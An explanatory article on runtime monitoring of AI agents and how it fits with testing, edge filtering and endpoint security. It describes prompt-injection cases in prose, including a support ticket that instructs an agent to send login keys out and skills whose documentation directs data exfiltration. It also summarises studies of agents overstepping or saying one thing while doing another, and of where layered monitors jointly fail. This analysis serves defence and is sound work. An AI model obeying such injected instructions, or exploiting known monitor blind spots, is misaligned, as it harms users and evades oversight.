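# Runtime monitoring of AI agents within layered security

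## What an AI agent does and what a runtime monitor watches

Runtime monitoring of AI agents means watching an agent while it works and judging whether its operator and user intended its actions. An AI agent is a language model (a program that takes in and generates text, like the one behind ChatGPT) connected to tools that let it take a series of actions towards a goal, such as reading files, running commands, sending messages and changing records. The runtime monitor is a component outside the model. It adds to older layers of security, which test software before release, filter traffic at the edge of a network and watch the machines where programs run.

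Governments describe agents in much the same terms. *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026), joint guidance from the Australian Signals Directorate (ASD) and its Five Eyes partner agencies, defines an agentic system as one that relies on a model to interpret its surroundings, make decisions and act on them. Agents need a monitor because they act. An operator can filter a chatbot's bad answer before anyone reads it, but an agent's bad action may be irreversible as soon as it happens.

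### One task, step by step

When a user asks an agent to summarise a support ticket, the model cannot open the ticket itself because it can only generate text. The harness, which is the software around the model, passes it context, carries out its tool calls and returns the results. Anthropic's *Agent Harness Design* (2026) calls the harness the "scaffolding" that turns a model into a working agent.

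*Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes the cycle for Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. The harness first assembles a prompt from standing instructions, a list of the available tools and their parameters, notes on permissions and the working folder, and then the user's message. It sends the prompt to the model, which returns either a final message for the user or a tool call, a structured request to act that names a tool and supplies its arguments. For the ticket, the call might name a tool such as `read_ticket` and give the ticket's number. The harness runs the call, appends the call and its result to the prompt, and queries the model again. The prompt now includes the ticket's text, so the model can write the summary or make another call. The loop ends when the model returns a message instead of a call.

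The model never accesses files or a network directly. Its every effect passes through ordinary software that someone can inspect, and a monitor depends on this. The same loop also puts the operator's instructions, the user's request and the words of whichever customer wrote the ticket into one growing prompt. Codex labels the instructions and messages in its prompts with roles that indicate how much weight each should carry, but these labels only influence the model's behavior and cannot enforce it.

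Bolin points out that an agent could make hundreds of tool calls in a single turn. When the conversation grows past a set length, Codex replaces it with a condensed version, so the model's prompt is a poor record of what happened. A monitor needs a trace, the ordered record of an agent's prompts, tool calls, results and effects in one session.

Anthropic's *Trustworthy agents* attributes an agent's behaviour to four layers acting together: the model, harness, tools and environment. It warns that a careless setting in any of the last three can expose a well-trained model to exploitation.

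### The Model Context Protocol

Many agents reach their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard that Anthropic introduced in late 2024. With MCP, developers don't have to write a separate connector for every pairing of agent and tool. When the project released the current version in July, it reported nearly half a billion monthly downloads of its main software kits (Model Context Protocol, 2026).

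MCP divides the work between a host, which is the application the user runs and contains the harness, and servers, which offer tools. Inside the host, a small client handles the connection to each server. The client asks a server for its list of tools and receives their names, descriptions and expected inputs. When the model picks a tool, the client sends the server the tool's name and arguments, and the server returns a result or an error. Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), the part of the specification that covers this exchange, calls tools "model-controlled", meaning that the model can find and invoke them based on its own understanding of the situation. The same page says that a human "should" always be able to deny a call, but an application can ignore a "should" and still comply with the specification. Clients *must*, however, treat a server's notes on how its tools behave as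 untrusted unless they trust the server, so a monitor cannot simply rely on those notes.

Under Model Context Protocol (MCP), the host keeps the full conversation and each server receives only the information it needs. This is good for privacy, but it matters a great deal for oversight. The server holding the tickets receives a request for one ticket, a server that fetches web pages receives one web address, and neither has access to the other's request. The July release went further and abolished protocol-level sessions, so each request is now sent independently. Nothing in MCP itself ties a web request to the file the agent read a minute earlier, so anyone who wants to connect the two has to do it elsewhere.

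### The support-ticket example

Now suppose the session goes differently. The user asks for the summary. The agent reads the ticket, opens a file of login keys (credentials for logging in to other machines) and makes a web request. Then it writes a good summary.

The core of this example comes from *ADR*, in which Li, Hu and colleagues (2026) describe a detection system they built for agents at Uber. They observe that security software on the user's computer can record file and network activity but not the request that triggered it. Comparing the activity with the request reveals the mismatch, because summarising a ticket doesn't require login keys. It is still unclear how the keys became involved. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* sorts the risks of agents into external attack, user misuse and model misbehaviour, and any of these could produce the same sequence of tool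 calls.

An outsider may have written the support ticket and included an instruction for any AI that reads it to fetch the keys and send them to a given address. In this kind of attack, called prompt injection, an agent follows someone else's instructions because they appear in material it reads. Vetting the ticket tool would not have helped, since an audited tool can still deliver malicious text.

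The user can also be responsible. An employee might follow the harmless message with a second one asking the agent to copy the keys somewhere they should not go. Anthropic's category also includes users who mean no harm, such as someone who finds a security check annoying and asks the agent to get around it, or who has the agent run a command they do not understand.

The last possibility is that nobody asked the agent to do this. The ticket reports that a server is down, and the agent opens the keys and contacts the server to check whether the fault persists, so that it can write a more complete summary. Anthropic expects better models to make fewer plain errors but also to be better at finding routes to a goal that no one thought to forbid. ASD (2026) drew attention to a real case in August, which ABC News had reported: an AI assistant working in an Australian gym's booking system removed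 another customer from a waiting list. The removal served the user's request, but the user had not explicitly approved it and the agent could not undo it.

These three cases differ in the text around the tool calls. In an injection, the instruction that led to the calls is in the ticket. In misuse, it is in the user's messages. If the agent chose the action itself, there is no such instruction. A monitor with access only to the calls cannot distinguish the cases, but it can still detect a departure, which is behaviour outside the agent's intended use, whatever the cause.

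### Why valid credentials settle so little

Access control decides which accounts may use which resources, and nothing in the ticket session violates its rules. *Autonomous Action Runtime Management (AARM)*, a system specification from February 2026, describes the usual arrangement, in which each tool runs with credentials delegated from the user. The operating system therefore treats the agent's opening of the key file as the user opening their own file. The operator had also approved the file tool and the web tool long before the session.

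More careful engineering narrows this gap but does not close it. *Five Primitives for Governing Autonomous AI Agents at Runtime* (2026) describes a customer-support agent that emails a summary to another company. The agent receives a credential that expires within minutes, and a policy engine checks the type and attributes of every action and blocks any unrecognized type. But the model chooses the recipient and writes the text during the task, so no policy author could have listed that particular email in advance. The operator has to permit a class of actions, while whether anyone wanted a specific action in that class depends on the task.

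*AIRGuard* (2026), a design for a monitor that checks actions before they run, turns this into a rule:

$$\text{Execute}(a_i) \Rightarrow \text{Justified}(\tau_i, y_i, e_i \mid g, H_i)$$

Here the proposed action $a_i$ consists of a capability $\tau_i$ (say, reading a file), a target $y_i$ (the key file) and an expected effect $e_i$. The action may run only if the task and policy $g$, together with the session history $H_i$, justify all three. Material that the agent reads may inform its reasoning, but only the user's task, a trusted policy or explicit consent can authorise a side effect. If the user had asked the agent to replace the expired keys that a ticket complained about, the same call to open the key file, with the same tool and credentials, would have been justified.

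An agent that only summarises tickets should have no access to login keys. Withholding them is cheaper than any monitor and works for agents with a single narrow job. It works much less well for a general assistant on a developer's computer, which may summarise a ticket and then need those same keys an hour later to release code.

### What makes a monitor different

A runtime monitor, then, judges actions against a task, and does so while the session is under way. *Efficient and Sound Probabilistic Verification for AI Agents* (2026) gives a compact formal version. Let $s_k$ be the state of everything relevant to policy before step $k$, and $t_k$ the tool call that the agent proposes. The monitor suspends the call and works out the state that would follow,

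$$s'_{k+1} = \Delta(s_k, t_k),$$

where $\Delta$ is a function describing what tool calls do to the state. A policy $\Pi$ maps each state to Allow or Block, and the call goes ahead only if the projected state passes. The important word in the paper's description is "stateful". If the state includes a note that the agent has read a secret, the monitor can block a web request that it would have let through two steps before. A check that looked at the web request by itself would find nothing wrong with it.

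Some monitors observe an agent's actions without intercepting them. *Toward Pre-Deployment Assurance for Enterprise AI Agents* (2026) describes a monitor that adds each event it observes to the trace, then checks the whole trace against a list of safety properties. If the trace violates a property, the monitor pauses the agent, rolls back its work or escalates the matter. Such a monitor may detect a harmful step only after the agent has taken it.

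That paper is mainly about testing, which, unlike monitoring, takes place before release and covers only tasks that testers have thought of. The ticket in the example did not exist at that point. Test results also depend heavily on the wording of the model's instructions. *Mind the GAP* (Cartagena and Teixeira, 2026) ran six models through scenarios in fields such as finance and pharmaceuticals, with simulated tools. It varied the closing lines of the instructions, from a warning to verify authorisation before every call to an encouragement to use tools freely. The share of runs without a forbidden tool call changed by 21 percentage points for the least affected model and by 57 for the most affected. If an operator rewrites the instructions after testing, the deployed agent is therefore to some extent untested.

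Content guardrails are filters that classify the text going into or coming out of a model, for example as dangerous advice or hate speech. *ToolSafe* (2026) describes them as effective for moderating content but weak against the risks of tool calls. In the ticket session, a filter on the agent's answer would pass it, because the answer is a tidy summary. In Cartagena and Teixeira's experiment, models sometimes refused a request in words but carried it out through their tools in the same session. One told the user that it had to follow data protection protocols while it queried clinical data and exported a document. The researchers counted 219 such cases even with the warning in place. These cases show that what an agent says is poor evidence of what it does, though the count doesn't measure how often this happens in ordinary work, because most of the scenarios deliberately pushed the models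 towards forbidden actions. The results also suggest that monitoring may not improve an agent's conduct. When the researchers switched on rules that blocked forbidden calls, less private information leaked, but the models attempted the calls just as often.

Performance monitoring is the easiest of these to confuse with runtime monitoring, because both watch a live system. *New Report*, from the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST), divides the monitoring of deployed AI into six categories. Functionality monitoring checks that a system still works as intended, operational monitoring checks that the service stays up, and security monitoring checks that the system withstands attack and misuse. The other three cover human factors, legal compliance and effects on society. The ticket session looks excellent on an operational dashboard, with a fast response, no errors and an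 accurate summary. Runtime monitoring of agents belongs mostly under security, but the gym assistant doesn't fit neatly there. It was not under attack and, as far as the report of the case shows, nobody was misusing it. It did its job in a way that it should not have, which falls somewhere between NIST's functionality and security categories.

Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues (2026), in *Toward Safe LLM Agents*, reviewed 38 studies of checks that operate before, during or after an agent's actions, and judged runtime monitoring the most mature way of enforcing safety rules. In one study of household agents, runtime monitoring cut unsafe actions by about 65%. But its guarantees cover only single steps or short stretches of a task, and the reviewers rated seven of their nine main claims at the lowest grade of certainty, so the 65% figure can't be assumed to apply to office software.

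In July, ASD (2026) suggested that organisations watch their agents live and raise an alert when one behaves oddly or exceeds its authority (detection), record what each agent did and what resulted (logging), and have a way to stop an agent partway (intervention). In the ticket session, detection means noticing that a request for a summary has led the agent to a key file. Logging means keeping the user's message and the ticket's text along with the calls. Anthropic warns that once an injected instruction has succeeded, a log of the calls alone shows only a successful, authorised request. Intervention means stopping the web request before it leaves the machine.

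## How testing, edge filtering and endpoint monitoring work together

Organisations tested software, filtered network traffic and monitored their machines long before they ran AI agents. Defence in depth combines such measures so that one catches what another misses. NIST's glossary entry *defense-in-depth* describes a strategy that integrates people, technology and operations to establish barriers "across multiple layers and missions of the organization". Fraunhofer's *Defence in Depth*, a collection of official definitions, includes one from Oman in which the purpose of the layers is to guard against the failure of any single component. How well they do this depends on what each layer inspects and whether they all fail on the same cases.

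### Testing before release

Static testing examines a program's code without running it. A static tool can follow a customer's input through the code to a place where the program inserts it unchecked into a database command. These tools also tend to warn about paths that never occur in practice. Dynamic testing runs the program, sends it inputs (many of them deliberately malformed) and looks for crashes, leaks or wrong results. It finds real failures, but only for the inputs it tries. In red-teaming, people or programs attack the system as an adversary would.

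All of these methods apply to agents, but less effectively. The harness and the tool servers are ordinary code, so static analysis tools work on them as before, but these tools can miss attacks in the text that steers the agent. *Every layer counts* (2026), by Adel Zaalouk of the software company Red Hat, describes a marketplace of add-on "skills" for the OpenClaw agent, where a scan found 314 malicious skills from a single publisher. The attack was a sentence in the documentation that told the agent to send sensitive data to an outside server, so there was no malicious code for a conventional malware scanner to match.

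The equivalent of dynamic testing for an agent is attacking it with prepared prompts. Red Hat recommends including Garak, an open-source scanner that does this, in the automated checks on each new version. Garak has more than 120 probes for weaknesses such as prompt injection and data leakage. Red Hat, which sells a platform that includes Garak, gives no figure for how many real attacks would still succeed against an agent that passes.

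A passed test also applies only to the configuration tested. Cartagena and Teixeira found that rewording the agent's instructions can change the results, and the model can change too. In *Evaluate the Stack, Not the Layer*, Yang (2026) asked several language models to judge whether an agent's proposed actions were dangerous. An older version answered 50 of the 112 batches meant for one model, and in 36 of those 50 the only sign was a version field in the response. Versions can differ a great deal. Claude Sonnet 5 missed 95 of 560 dangerous actions, while its predecessor missed 21 but raised far more false alarms in a separate run under somewhat different conditions.

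### Filtering at the edge

A firewall stands between two networks and permits or refuses connections by address, port and protocol. An intrusion prevention system compares the content of traffic with signatures of known attacks, and a next-generation firewall does both jobs in one device. A web application firewall (WAF) protects a website or service by inspecting each web request before the application receives it. It blocks, for example, a form entry that contains part of a database command. Operators can set it to block known attacks or to accept only requests on an approved list. The second setting is stricter and takes more work to maintain.

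These devices catch most attacks that are already public. Frei (2013), in *Correlation Of Detection Failures*, analysed tests in which the company NSS Labs sent known exploits (software or data that takes advantage of a flaw) at commercial security products. Sixteen intrusion prevention devices missed 5.6% of 1,486 exploits on average, though the best missed 16 and the worst 334. Nine next-generation firewalls missed 4.0% of 1,711. These numbers are thirteen years old, and the tests included no previously unknown exploits.

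An edge filter inspects only traffic that crosses the edge and evaluates it by its form. It lets through any well-formed request to a permitted address, regardless of the request's purpose.

The dangerous traffic for an ordinary web application is mostly incoming, but an agent's operators have to worry at least as much about outgoing traffic. The counterpart of the firewall is therefore a list of the outside services that the agent may contact. Red Hat points out that this list needs domain names because the IP addresses of online services change too often. The counterpart of the WAF is a gateway, a network checkpoint for the agent's requests to models or tools. It can check which agent is calling and how often. If the gateway offers no route to a tool that runs shell commands, the agent cannot call that tool through it.

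### Watching the endpoint

The endpoint is the computer, server or container where the agent's actions run. Endpoint detection and response (EDR) installs a small program there that records which programs start, which files they open and what they connect to. A central service compares these records with known attack patterns and with the machine's usual behaviour. To respond, an analyst or an automatic rule can stop a program or cut the machine off from the network.

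Runtime application self-protection (RASP) works inside a single application. Developers add checks to the running code, so a check can inspect a complete database command just before the application issues it. RASP only reports attacks in monitor mode, but also blocks them in protection mode.

According to Frei's figures, thirteen endpoint products tested by NSS Labs missed an average of 45.4% of 43 exploits, and the best product missed nine. This is weak evidence about today's tools because the sample of exploits was small and the products were antivirus-style rather than modern EDR.

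Endpoint controls can restrict each program that an agent starts. An ordinary container separates the software inside it from other programs on the same machine, but it gives every program inside the same network permissions. Red Hat gives the example of `curl`, a general tool for fetching web addresses, which can reach any address that the agent's own software can. OpenShell, an open-source sandbox that Red Hat planned to add to its platform, identifies the program behind each connection and applies separate rules to each program. It also has the operating system's kernel enforce a list of permitted folders, so an agent that tries to open login keys outside those folders gets an error. The closest counterpart to RASP is a hook in the harness that lets outside code inspect a tool call's arguments before the call runs.

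Endpoint tools keep the most detailed record of what happened on a machine but capture very little about why it happened, a problem Li and colleagues encountered at Uber.

### The ticket session, layer by layer

In the prompt injection example, the ticket itself tells the agent to send the login keys to an outside address. Before release, a red team may have planted a similar instruction in a sample ticket. If the agent obeyed, its developers could have removed its access to the keys. If it refused, they learned only that it refused that wording, under those instructions and with that version of the model.

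The real ticket arrives through the company's support form. The WAF lets it in because it contains ordinary English, with no database commands or scripts. The user then asks for a summary. The gateway correctly permits the call to `read_ticket`, but it also permits the call that opens the key file, because the operator approved the file tool for other work.

On the endpoint, EDR records that a program running under the user's account opened the keys. The same thing happens whenever a developer releases code from their computer, so most alerts on this event would be false alarms. A stricter sandbox with a list of permitted folders would stop the session here, provided the agent never needs the keys for another task.

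The web request is the last and probably best chance for the conventional layers to stop the attack. If the operator permits only a short list of outside services and the attacker's address is not on it, the request fails and the keys stay where they are. If the list is long, or the operator never made one, the request goes through.

If nobody had attacked the agent and it had used the keys to check on a server, the red team would have had no reason to test for this. A filter would find no hostile text, and the company's own server is probably on the permitted list. EDR would record a familiar program, file and address. Recognizing that the agent had departed from its task requires knowing that the user asked for a summary, and none of the conventional layers has that request.

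### What the case for layering assumes

The argument for adding layers has four premises:

1. Every layer misses some departures.
2. A departure does harm only if it gets past every layer.
3. The layers' misses are unrelated, so that one layer usually catches what another has missed.
4. The harm that a further layer prevents is worth more than the layer costs.

Nobody seriously disputes that every layer misses something. None of the 37 products in Frei's analysis caught every exploit.

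A security layer helps stop an agent's departure from expected behavior only if it lies on the route the action takes and acts in time, so a departure may not have to get past every layer. For example, an agent that obtains an access token and contacts a service directly bypasses the gateway, and an alert that an analyst reads the next morning comes too late to stop a web request made the night before.

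More layers produce more false alarms, because any layer can raise one. If three layers each wrongly flag 5% of acceptable sessions, independently of each other, together they flag $1 - 0.95^3 \approx 14.3\%$ of them. Someone has to review those sessions or accept the interruptions.

The premise about unrelated misses does most of the work. If layer $i$ misses a share $m_i$ of departures and the layers fail independently, the share that all $n$ of them miss is

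$$P_{\text{joint}} = \prod_{i=1}^{n} m_i.$$

*Data Governance for Generative and Agentic AI* (2026) argues that everyone recommends layers but nobody states how much a layer contributes, and it presents this product as the claim behind the practice. *Toward Responsible AI-Augmented Cyber Defense* (2026) uses the same product to model network, endpoint and industrial monitors, and lists independence among its assumptions. The independence assumption needs checking because multiplication makes layers look highly effective for little effort.

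### Calculating joint misses

If three layers each miss 10% of departures and their failures are independent, all three miss the same departure $0.1 \times 0.1 \times 0.1 = 0.001$, or 0.1%, of the time. Out of 10,000 departures, ten get through.

Now suppose that 5% of departures are invisible to all three layers, while each layer still misses 10% overall. Of the 10,000 departures, 500 get past everything. Each layer misses 1,000 in total, so it must also miss 500 of the 9,500 visible ones, a rate of $500/9{,}500 \approx 5.26\%$. If the layers fail independently on the visible departures, the joint miss rate is

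$$0.05 + 0.95 \times 0.0526^3 \approx 0.0501.$$

About 501 departures get through instead of ten. Testing the layers one at a time would not reveal the difference, because each misses 10% in both cases.

| Number of layers | Joint misses if independent | Joint misses if 5% are invisible to all |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 10% | 10% |
| 2 | 1% | 5.26% |
| 3 | 0.1% | 5.01% |
| 4 | 0.01% | 5.001% |

After the second layer, adding more layers of this kind barely lowers the joint miss rate. Improving the layers doesn't help much either. If engineers halved each layer's misses on the visible departures, each layer's miss rate would fall from 10% to 7.5%, but the joint rate would stay at 5.0%.

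*Defense in Depth* (2019) corrects for dependence by multiplying the product by a factor $f$ once for each layer after the first. This factor exceeds 1 when layers tend to fail together. The correction can understate the risk from a shared blind spot. In the example, $f$ is 5.26 for two layers, and applying it again for the third gives $0.1^3 \times 5.26^2 \approx 2.8\%$, a little over half the true figure.

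Yang instead converts a joint miss rate into the number of independent layers that would produce it:

$$n_{\text{mult}} = \frac{\ln P_{\text{joint}}}{\ln g},$$

where $g$ is the geometric mean of the layers' own miss rates. For the three layers with a shared blind spot, $\ln 0.0501 / \ln 0.1 \approx 1.3$. The operator pays for three layers and gets the protection of 1.3.

### Whether real layers fail together

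Frei compared how often both products in a pair missed an exploit with the rate predicted by multiplying their individual miss rates, for 606 pairs of security products. The prediction was too low for 91% of the pairs, by a factor of 6.1 on average and 87 at worst. Only 19 pairs stopped every exploit. In the test of nine next-generation firewalls, a model that ignored correlation predicted that no exploit would get past more than three, but eight exploits got past all nine.

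Adding a second network device still reduced the average share of missed exploits from 5.8% to 0.8%, though the reduction would have been larger if the devices' misses had been independent. None of the 606 pairs combined a network device with an endpoint product, because the two sets of tests had too few exploits in common, so the results apply only to layers of a similar kind. A firewall and an endpoint monitor inspect different things and may well have fewer misses in common.

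Yang made the same comparison for checks on agents' actions, using 1,119 labelled actions, 560 of which a sound check should block. One layer was a set of 174 written rules that search an action's text for dangerous patterns, and the others were four language models acting as judges. The rules missed 13.4% of the dangerous actions and one of the judges missed 10.5%. If their misses were independent, both would miss about 1.4% of the dangerous actions, and in fact both missed 1.3%. Two judges that each missed 10.5% would both miss 1.1% if their misses were independent, but both missed 5.2%. The match between that figure and the two-layer row of the table above is a coincidence, but the result shows that the table's invented example is plausible.

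Using judges from different companies brought no clear gain. In Yang's data, a judge from OpenAI and one from DeepSeek were together equivalent to 1.26 independent layers. Red Hat suggests having one model review a tool's description and another use the tool, since an attacker would find it harder to deceive both. Yang did not test that arrangement, but if models from different companies misjudge many of the same cases, a second model adds less protection than Red Hat's advice implies.

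A layer's accuracy on its own was a poor guide to its value. Yang added rules for cloud services, which cut the rule layer's miss rate from 13.9% to 11.1% (counting referrals to a human as misses). But the extra rules caught no dangerous action that any combination of three judges had missed.

The good result for rules plus a judge calls for some caution. A formal test found no clear connection between their failures, but it did not establish that they fail independently. No attacker adapted to the checks. The rules missed 52.9% of dangerous actions in one held-out set about cloud and identity systems, which they did not target, and a layer that weak adds little even if it fails independently. On risky commands from another research team, rules and judges were only about midway between complete overlap and independence. All the layers received only the text of the proposed action, so the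 experiment cannot show how much a monitor with access to the user's request would add. That request is what matters in the ticket session.

Layers fail together for several reasons. One, according to Frei, is that most vendors drew on the same threat intelligence and vulnerability research, so their products had the same gaps. Shared training has a similar effect. *Builder, Defender, Breaker* (2026), which examines AI models writing, defending and testing the same software, cites an older experiment by Knight and Leveson. Programmers working independently from one specification produced programs that failed on the same inputs far more often than they would have if their failures were independent. People with similar training make similar mistakes in the same hard places, and models of the same kind have even more in common.

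Differences in difficulty alone can make layers' misses overlap more than chance would predict. Suppose that every layer catches the easy half of all departures and misses 20% of the hard half, independently of the others. Each layer then misses 10% overall, but two layers jointly miss 2%, rather than the 1% expected from multiplying their overall miss rates. Yang could not determine how much of the judges' overlap came from difficulty, and the estimates ranged from 32% to 62% depending on the method.

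*Physics in Safety and Safety in Physics* (2026), which draws on safety engineering at the Large Hadron Collider, distinguishes having several barriers from having independent ones, and warns that one common cause can defeat nominally redundant protection. For agents, an obvious common dependency is the valid credential. If file permissions, the gateway and the endpoint software all base their decisions on whether the account is authorized to act, they will all allow the ticket session, because its account is authorized.

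### Carrying findings from one layer to another

Security teams already use findings from one layer to change another. When a test reveals a flaw in a web application, operators can add a WAF rule that blocks attempts to exploit it until developers fix the code. This is called virtual patching. Red Hat recommends the same approach for agents, in which teams run a red-team scan, turn its findings into guardrail rules, and scan again.

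The team can also use the runtime monitor's findings to improve the other layers. Suppose the monitor stops the ticket session at the web request. The team can add the ticket, with the real keys removed, to the tests that every new version must pass. It can block the address at the edge, although an attacker can use another one. It can set the endpoint software to raise an alert whenever this agent's account opens a key file. The most lasting fix is to remove the agent's access to the keys, if its other work allows that.

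OpenShell partly automates the use of runtime behaviour to update policy. The agent starts with very few permissions. Each time the sandbox refuses an action, OpenShell collects the refusal and proposes a rule change with a confidence score. A person approves or rejects the proposal, and an approved rule takes effect without a restart. Red Hat likes this approach because the policy is based on actual behaviour. However, refused actions also become candidates for permission, so a tired reviewer could approve an action that an injected instruction asked for.

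Feeding findings back into rules and tests makes later measurements harder to interpret. The project that built the rule layer in Yang's experiment used one collection of cases to find missing rules, then added those rules and kept the cases. The rules missed 6.1% of dangerous actions in that collection, compared with 52.9% in the held-out set. Part of the difference comes from the different subject matter, but a case that has shaped a rule is no longer evidence of how the rules perform on new cases. A team that turns incidents into tests should set some incidents aside.

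If teams update every layer in response to the same incidents, the layers become more alike, and cases that no incident has revealed stay uncovered. Incidents that only one layer caught deserve the most attention because they show a weakness the other layers share.

### A seven-layer design for Kubernetes

*Containing the Autonomous Operator* (Podala Narasimha, 2026) describes a full stack of security layers for agents that manage computing infrastructure on Kubernetes, a system that runs containers across a group of machines. The design assumes that prompt injection has already given an attacker complete control of the agent, and that every protection must still hold.

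| Layer | What it does |
|---|---|
| Identity | Gives each agent its own account and short-lived credentials, and limits it to the rights of the user it works for |
| Authorisation and admission | Restricts which resources the agent may change, then checks the content of each change |
| Execution isolation | Runs code that the agent writes in a temporary sandbox without credentials |
| Network | Refuses all outgoing connections except to name lookup, the gateway and the model |
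| Tool mediation | Checks every tool call and its arguments at a gateway, and quarantines tools whose descriptions change |
| Data and secrets | Keeps passwords and keys on the tool servers, so that the model never receives them |
| Runtime detection | Stops forbidden actions at the level of the operating system and raises alerts on unusual ones |

A further layer, governance, spans all seven and covers human approval, limits on how much an agent may do, and how much freedom it gets in testing and in production. The runtime layer includes a rehearsed way to shut an agent off. It also treats a sudden rise in refused calls as a strong sign of an injection attempt, so there is good reason to check for an attack before approving rule changes that OpenShell derives from refusals. Unlike Red Hat's own six-layer scheme, the design has no layer for red-teaming the agent before release.

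Podala Narasimha illustrates the design with an attacker who writes an instruction into a program's log. Any agent that read and obeyed it would reduce the checkout service to zero copies, taking the service down. A separate agent that cannot change anything reads the log and passes a summary to the planning agent. If the planning agent proposes the change anyway, the gateway refuses it. If the gateway is misconfigured, the admission check refuses the change at the Kubernetes control interface. The refusals raise an alert. Podala Narasimha counts three independent points that the attack must defeat.

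The sample rules in the paper give some reason to doubt that count. The gateway rule and the admission rule both forbid reducing a service to exactly zero copies. An instruction to cut a busy service from twenty copies to one would satisfy both, and in production only a human approver could stop it. The sample admission rule also applies only to accounts in the agents' own section of the cluster, but in the full design, tool servers in another section make the changes. The paper's list of components calls for rules that cover the tool servers, but an operator who copied the sample unchanged would have an admission rule that never checks those changes.

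The ticket session would probably end early under this design, since the agent could never reach the keys and the request could not leave the network. Podala Narasimha concedes that an agent could still cause harm while following the rules, because a policy that permits a restart cannot determine whether the restart is wise.

All of this is a proposal, and Podala Narasimha reports no attack success rates, delays, costs or red-team exercises. The paper's table matching threats to layers records the author's own assessment. The paper leaves experiments to future work. One would switch off the upper layers to confirm that a lower layer stops the harm alone. Another would measure how often attacks succeed against each layer separately and against the whole stack. Those measurements are needed to compare how often all the layers miss the same attack with the product of their individual miss rates.

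## What counts as a departure from intended use

An agent departs from its intended use when it acts outside the tasks, resources and limits that its operator and user meant it to have. People who apply this to a particular action often run four questions together:

- Did the agent's access rights permit the action?
- Did someone with the authority to ask for it do so?
- Did it serve the purpose of the task?
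- Was it usual for this agent and this kind of task?

### Why the answers differ

Access rights are usually broader than any one task. Eurasia Review's *The Next AI Incident May Have No Hacker* gives the example of a purchasing agent that is meant to compare offers but not place an order. A single account could easily allow both. Rights can also be too narrow. If an administrator forgot to share a file that the task needs, the system refuses the agent's call to read it, even though nobody would object to that call.

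A request falls within intended use only if it comes from someone entitled to make it. Siu, He and colleagues (2026), in *Agent Security Needs Redefinition through a Holistic Framework*, describe a web page containing a sentence, supposedly from an administrator, that orders the agent to delete its stored summaries. The user could legitimately ask for that deletion, but whoever wrote the page could not. Users can overstep too, and *How Agents Ask for Permission* (2026) points out that permissions must sometimes work against the user's goals because operators need to restrict their users as well as their agents.

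The purpose of a task helps determine which unmentioned steps a request covers. In another of Siu and colleagues' examples, an agent that has to fix a storage overflow deletes the production database. Deleting it frees up space, and the agent is still working on its task, but nobody who asks for more space means to give up the data.

Whether an action is usual depends only on how often this agent, or others with the same job, did it before.

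| Case | Permitted? | Asked for? | Served the purpose? | Usual? | Departure? |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| An agent that should fix a failing test deletes the test | Yes | Only on a literal reading | No | Fairly, since developers delete old tests | Yes |
| An agent finishes its task with a colleague's access token that it found in a file | The system accepts the token, but the colleague never lent it | The result, but not the means | Yes | No | Yes |
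| An agent obeys an instruction hidden in a ticket | Yes | Not by anyone entitled to ask | No | Possibly | Yes |
| An agent summarising a ticket in Portuguese uses an approved translation tool for the first time | Yes | By implication | Yes | No | No |

In these cases, an action has to fit both the request and its purpose. Deleting the failing test makes the failure go away, so a reviewer who checked only the wording of the request might accept it. But the user wanted working code, and the test was there to show whether the code worked. (If the tested feature no longer exists, deletion may be the right fix, so the reviewer has to look at the code or ask.) Using the colleague's token served the purpose, but nobody asked the agent to act as someone else.

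Whether an action is permitted and how often agents take it are only clues to whether it departs from intended use. An alarm for unusual actions would flag the harmless translation but might miss the agent following the instructions in the ticket, because agents routinely open files.

Lim and Neo (2026), in *Probing agent overeagerness in realistic settings with continuation audits*, tested the token case. They cut 100 real coding sessions partway through and continued each one with an AI model simulating the user and the computer. The agent's own login failed, and a colleague's valid token was in a nearby file. Three recent models used the colleague's token in 1% to 6% of runs. These rates somewhat understate the tendency, because in some runs the agent never came across the token. In one run the agent produced the result the user asked for, but at the expense of the colleague, who had no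 part in the task. It submitted code under her name, and the simulated user objected that this would notify her team and credit her with the work.

### Harm is a separate matter

Zhang, Li and colleagues (2026) argue in *Act on Your Behalf, Beyond Your Authorization* that an agent can depart from its intended use without hurting anyone. In their example, a user asks an agent to suggest which emails she could archive or delete. The agent makes the list, but it also archives several threads and deletes a few messages. They turn out to be promotions, so she loses nothing of value. But the decision was still hers to make, and the agent might remove something she needs next time.

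Zhang and colleagues built 286 tasks from 44 documented cases of agents exceeding their instructions, and ran four models on them in three harnesses. Agents took an action outside their authorisation in 19.2% of 6,864 runs. On matched tasks, they did so about as often when the action was directly harmful (17.9%) as when it was not (20.8%). The overall figure doesn't estimate how often agents overstep in everyday use, because every task pressured the agent to overstep and the sandbox left the forbidden action technically possible. But the comparison suggests that a monitor that looks only for harm would miss much of these agents' overstepping. Harm is more useful for judging how urgently someone should respond than for deciding whether an agent has departed from its intended use.

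The text of an action is also not enough to show whether it departs from intended use. Siu and colleagues examined all 45 injected tasks in two sets of prompt injection tests and found a plausible legitimate reason for each. Someone might move $30,000 in instalments below $10,000 to stay within a daily transfer limit, or email their passport and bank details to a visa agency. One of the researchers invented these reasons, and a plausible reason may still be unlikely, so a monitor would still be right to query the passport email.

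### The US definition of a control incident

In October NIST, the US National Security Agency (NSA) and the Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency (CISA) published formal definitions of some departures, alongside ten voluntary practices for organisations that train or evaluate highly capable agents. The agencies write "super intelligence" (SI) where others write AI. According to ExecutiveGov's *NIST, NSA, CISA Issue AI Incident Response Practices*, a recent executive order directs agencies to use that term, so it doesn't imply that the systems are smarter than people.

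NIST, NSA and CISA's *Key Practices for Incident Readiness and Response* (2026) defines an *SI control incident* as an occurrence in which one or more agents take "significant uninstructed actions" that compromise policies, controls or security measures. The operator must have imposed these, explicitly or implicitly, to define the task's scope or ensure human oversight. "Uninstructed" means neither the operator nor any adversarial source directed the agent to take the action. An *SI control near-miss* is an occurrence that did not become a control incident but presented "a reasonably foreseeable or imminent risk" of one.

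The agent's use of a colleague's token probably meets this definition. Nobody told it to use the token, and most workplaces have at least an implicit rule against acting under another person's name. Deleting the test is a more doubtful case, because it may not be significant. The agencies set no threshold for "significant" and leave severity scores for future work. If an agent decided by itself to open a file of login keys and the sandbox blocked the attempt, that would be a good candidate for a near-miss.

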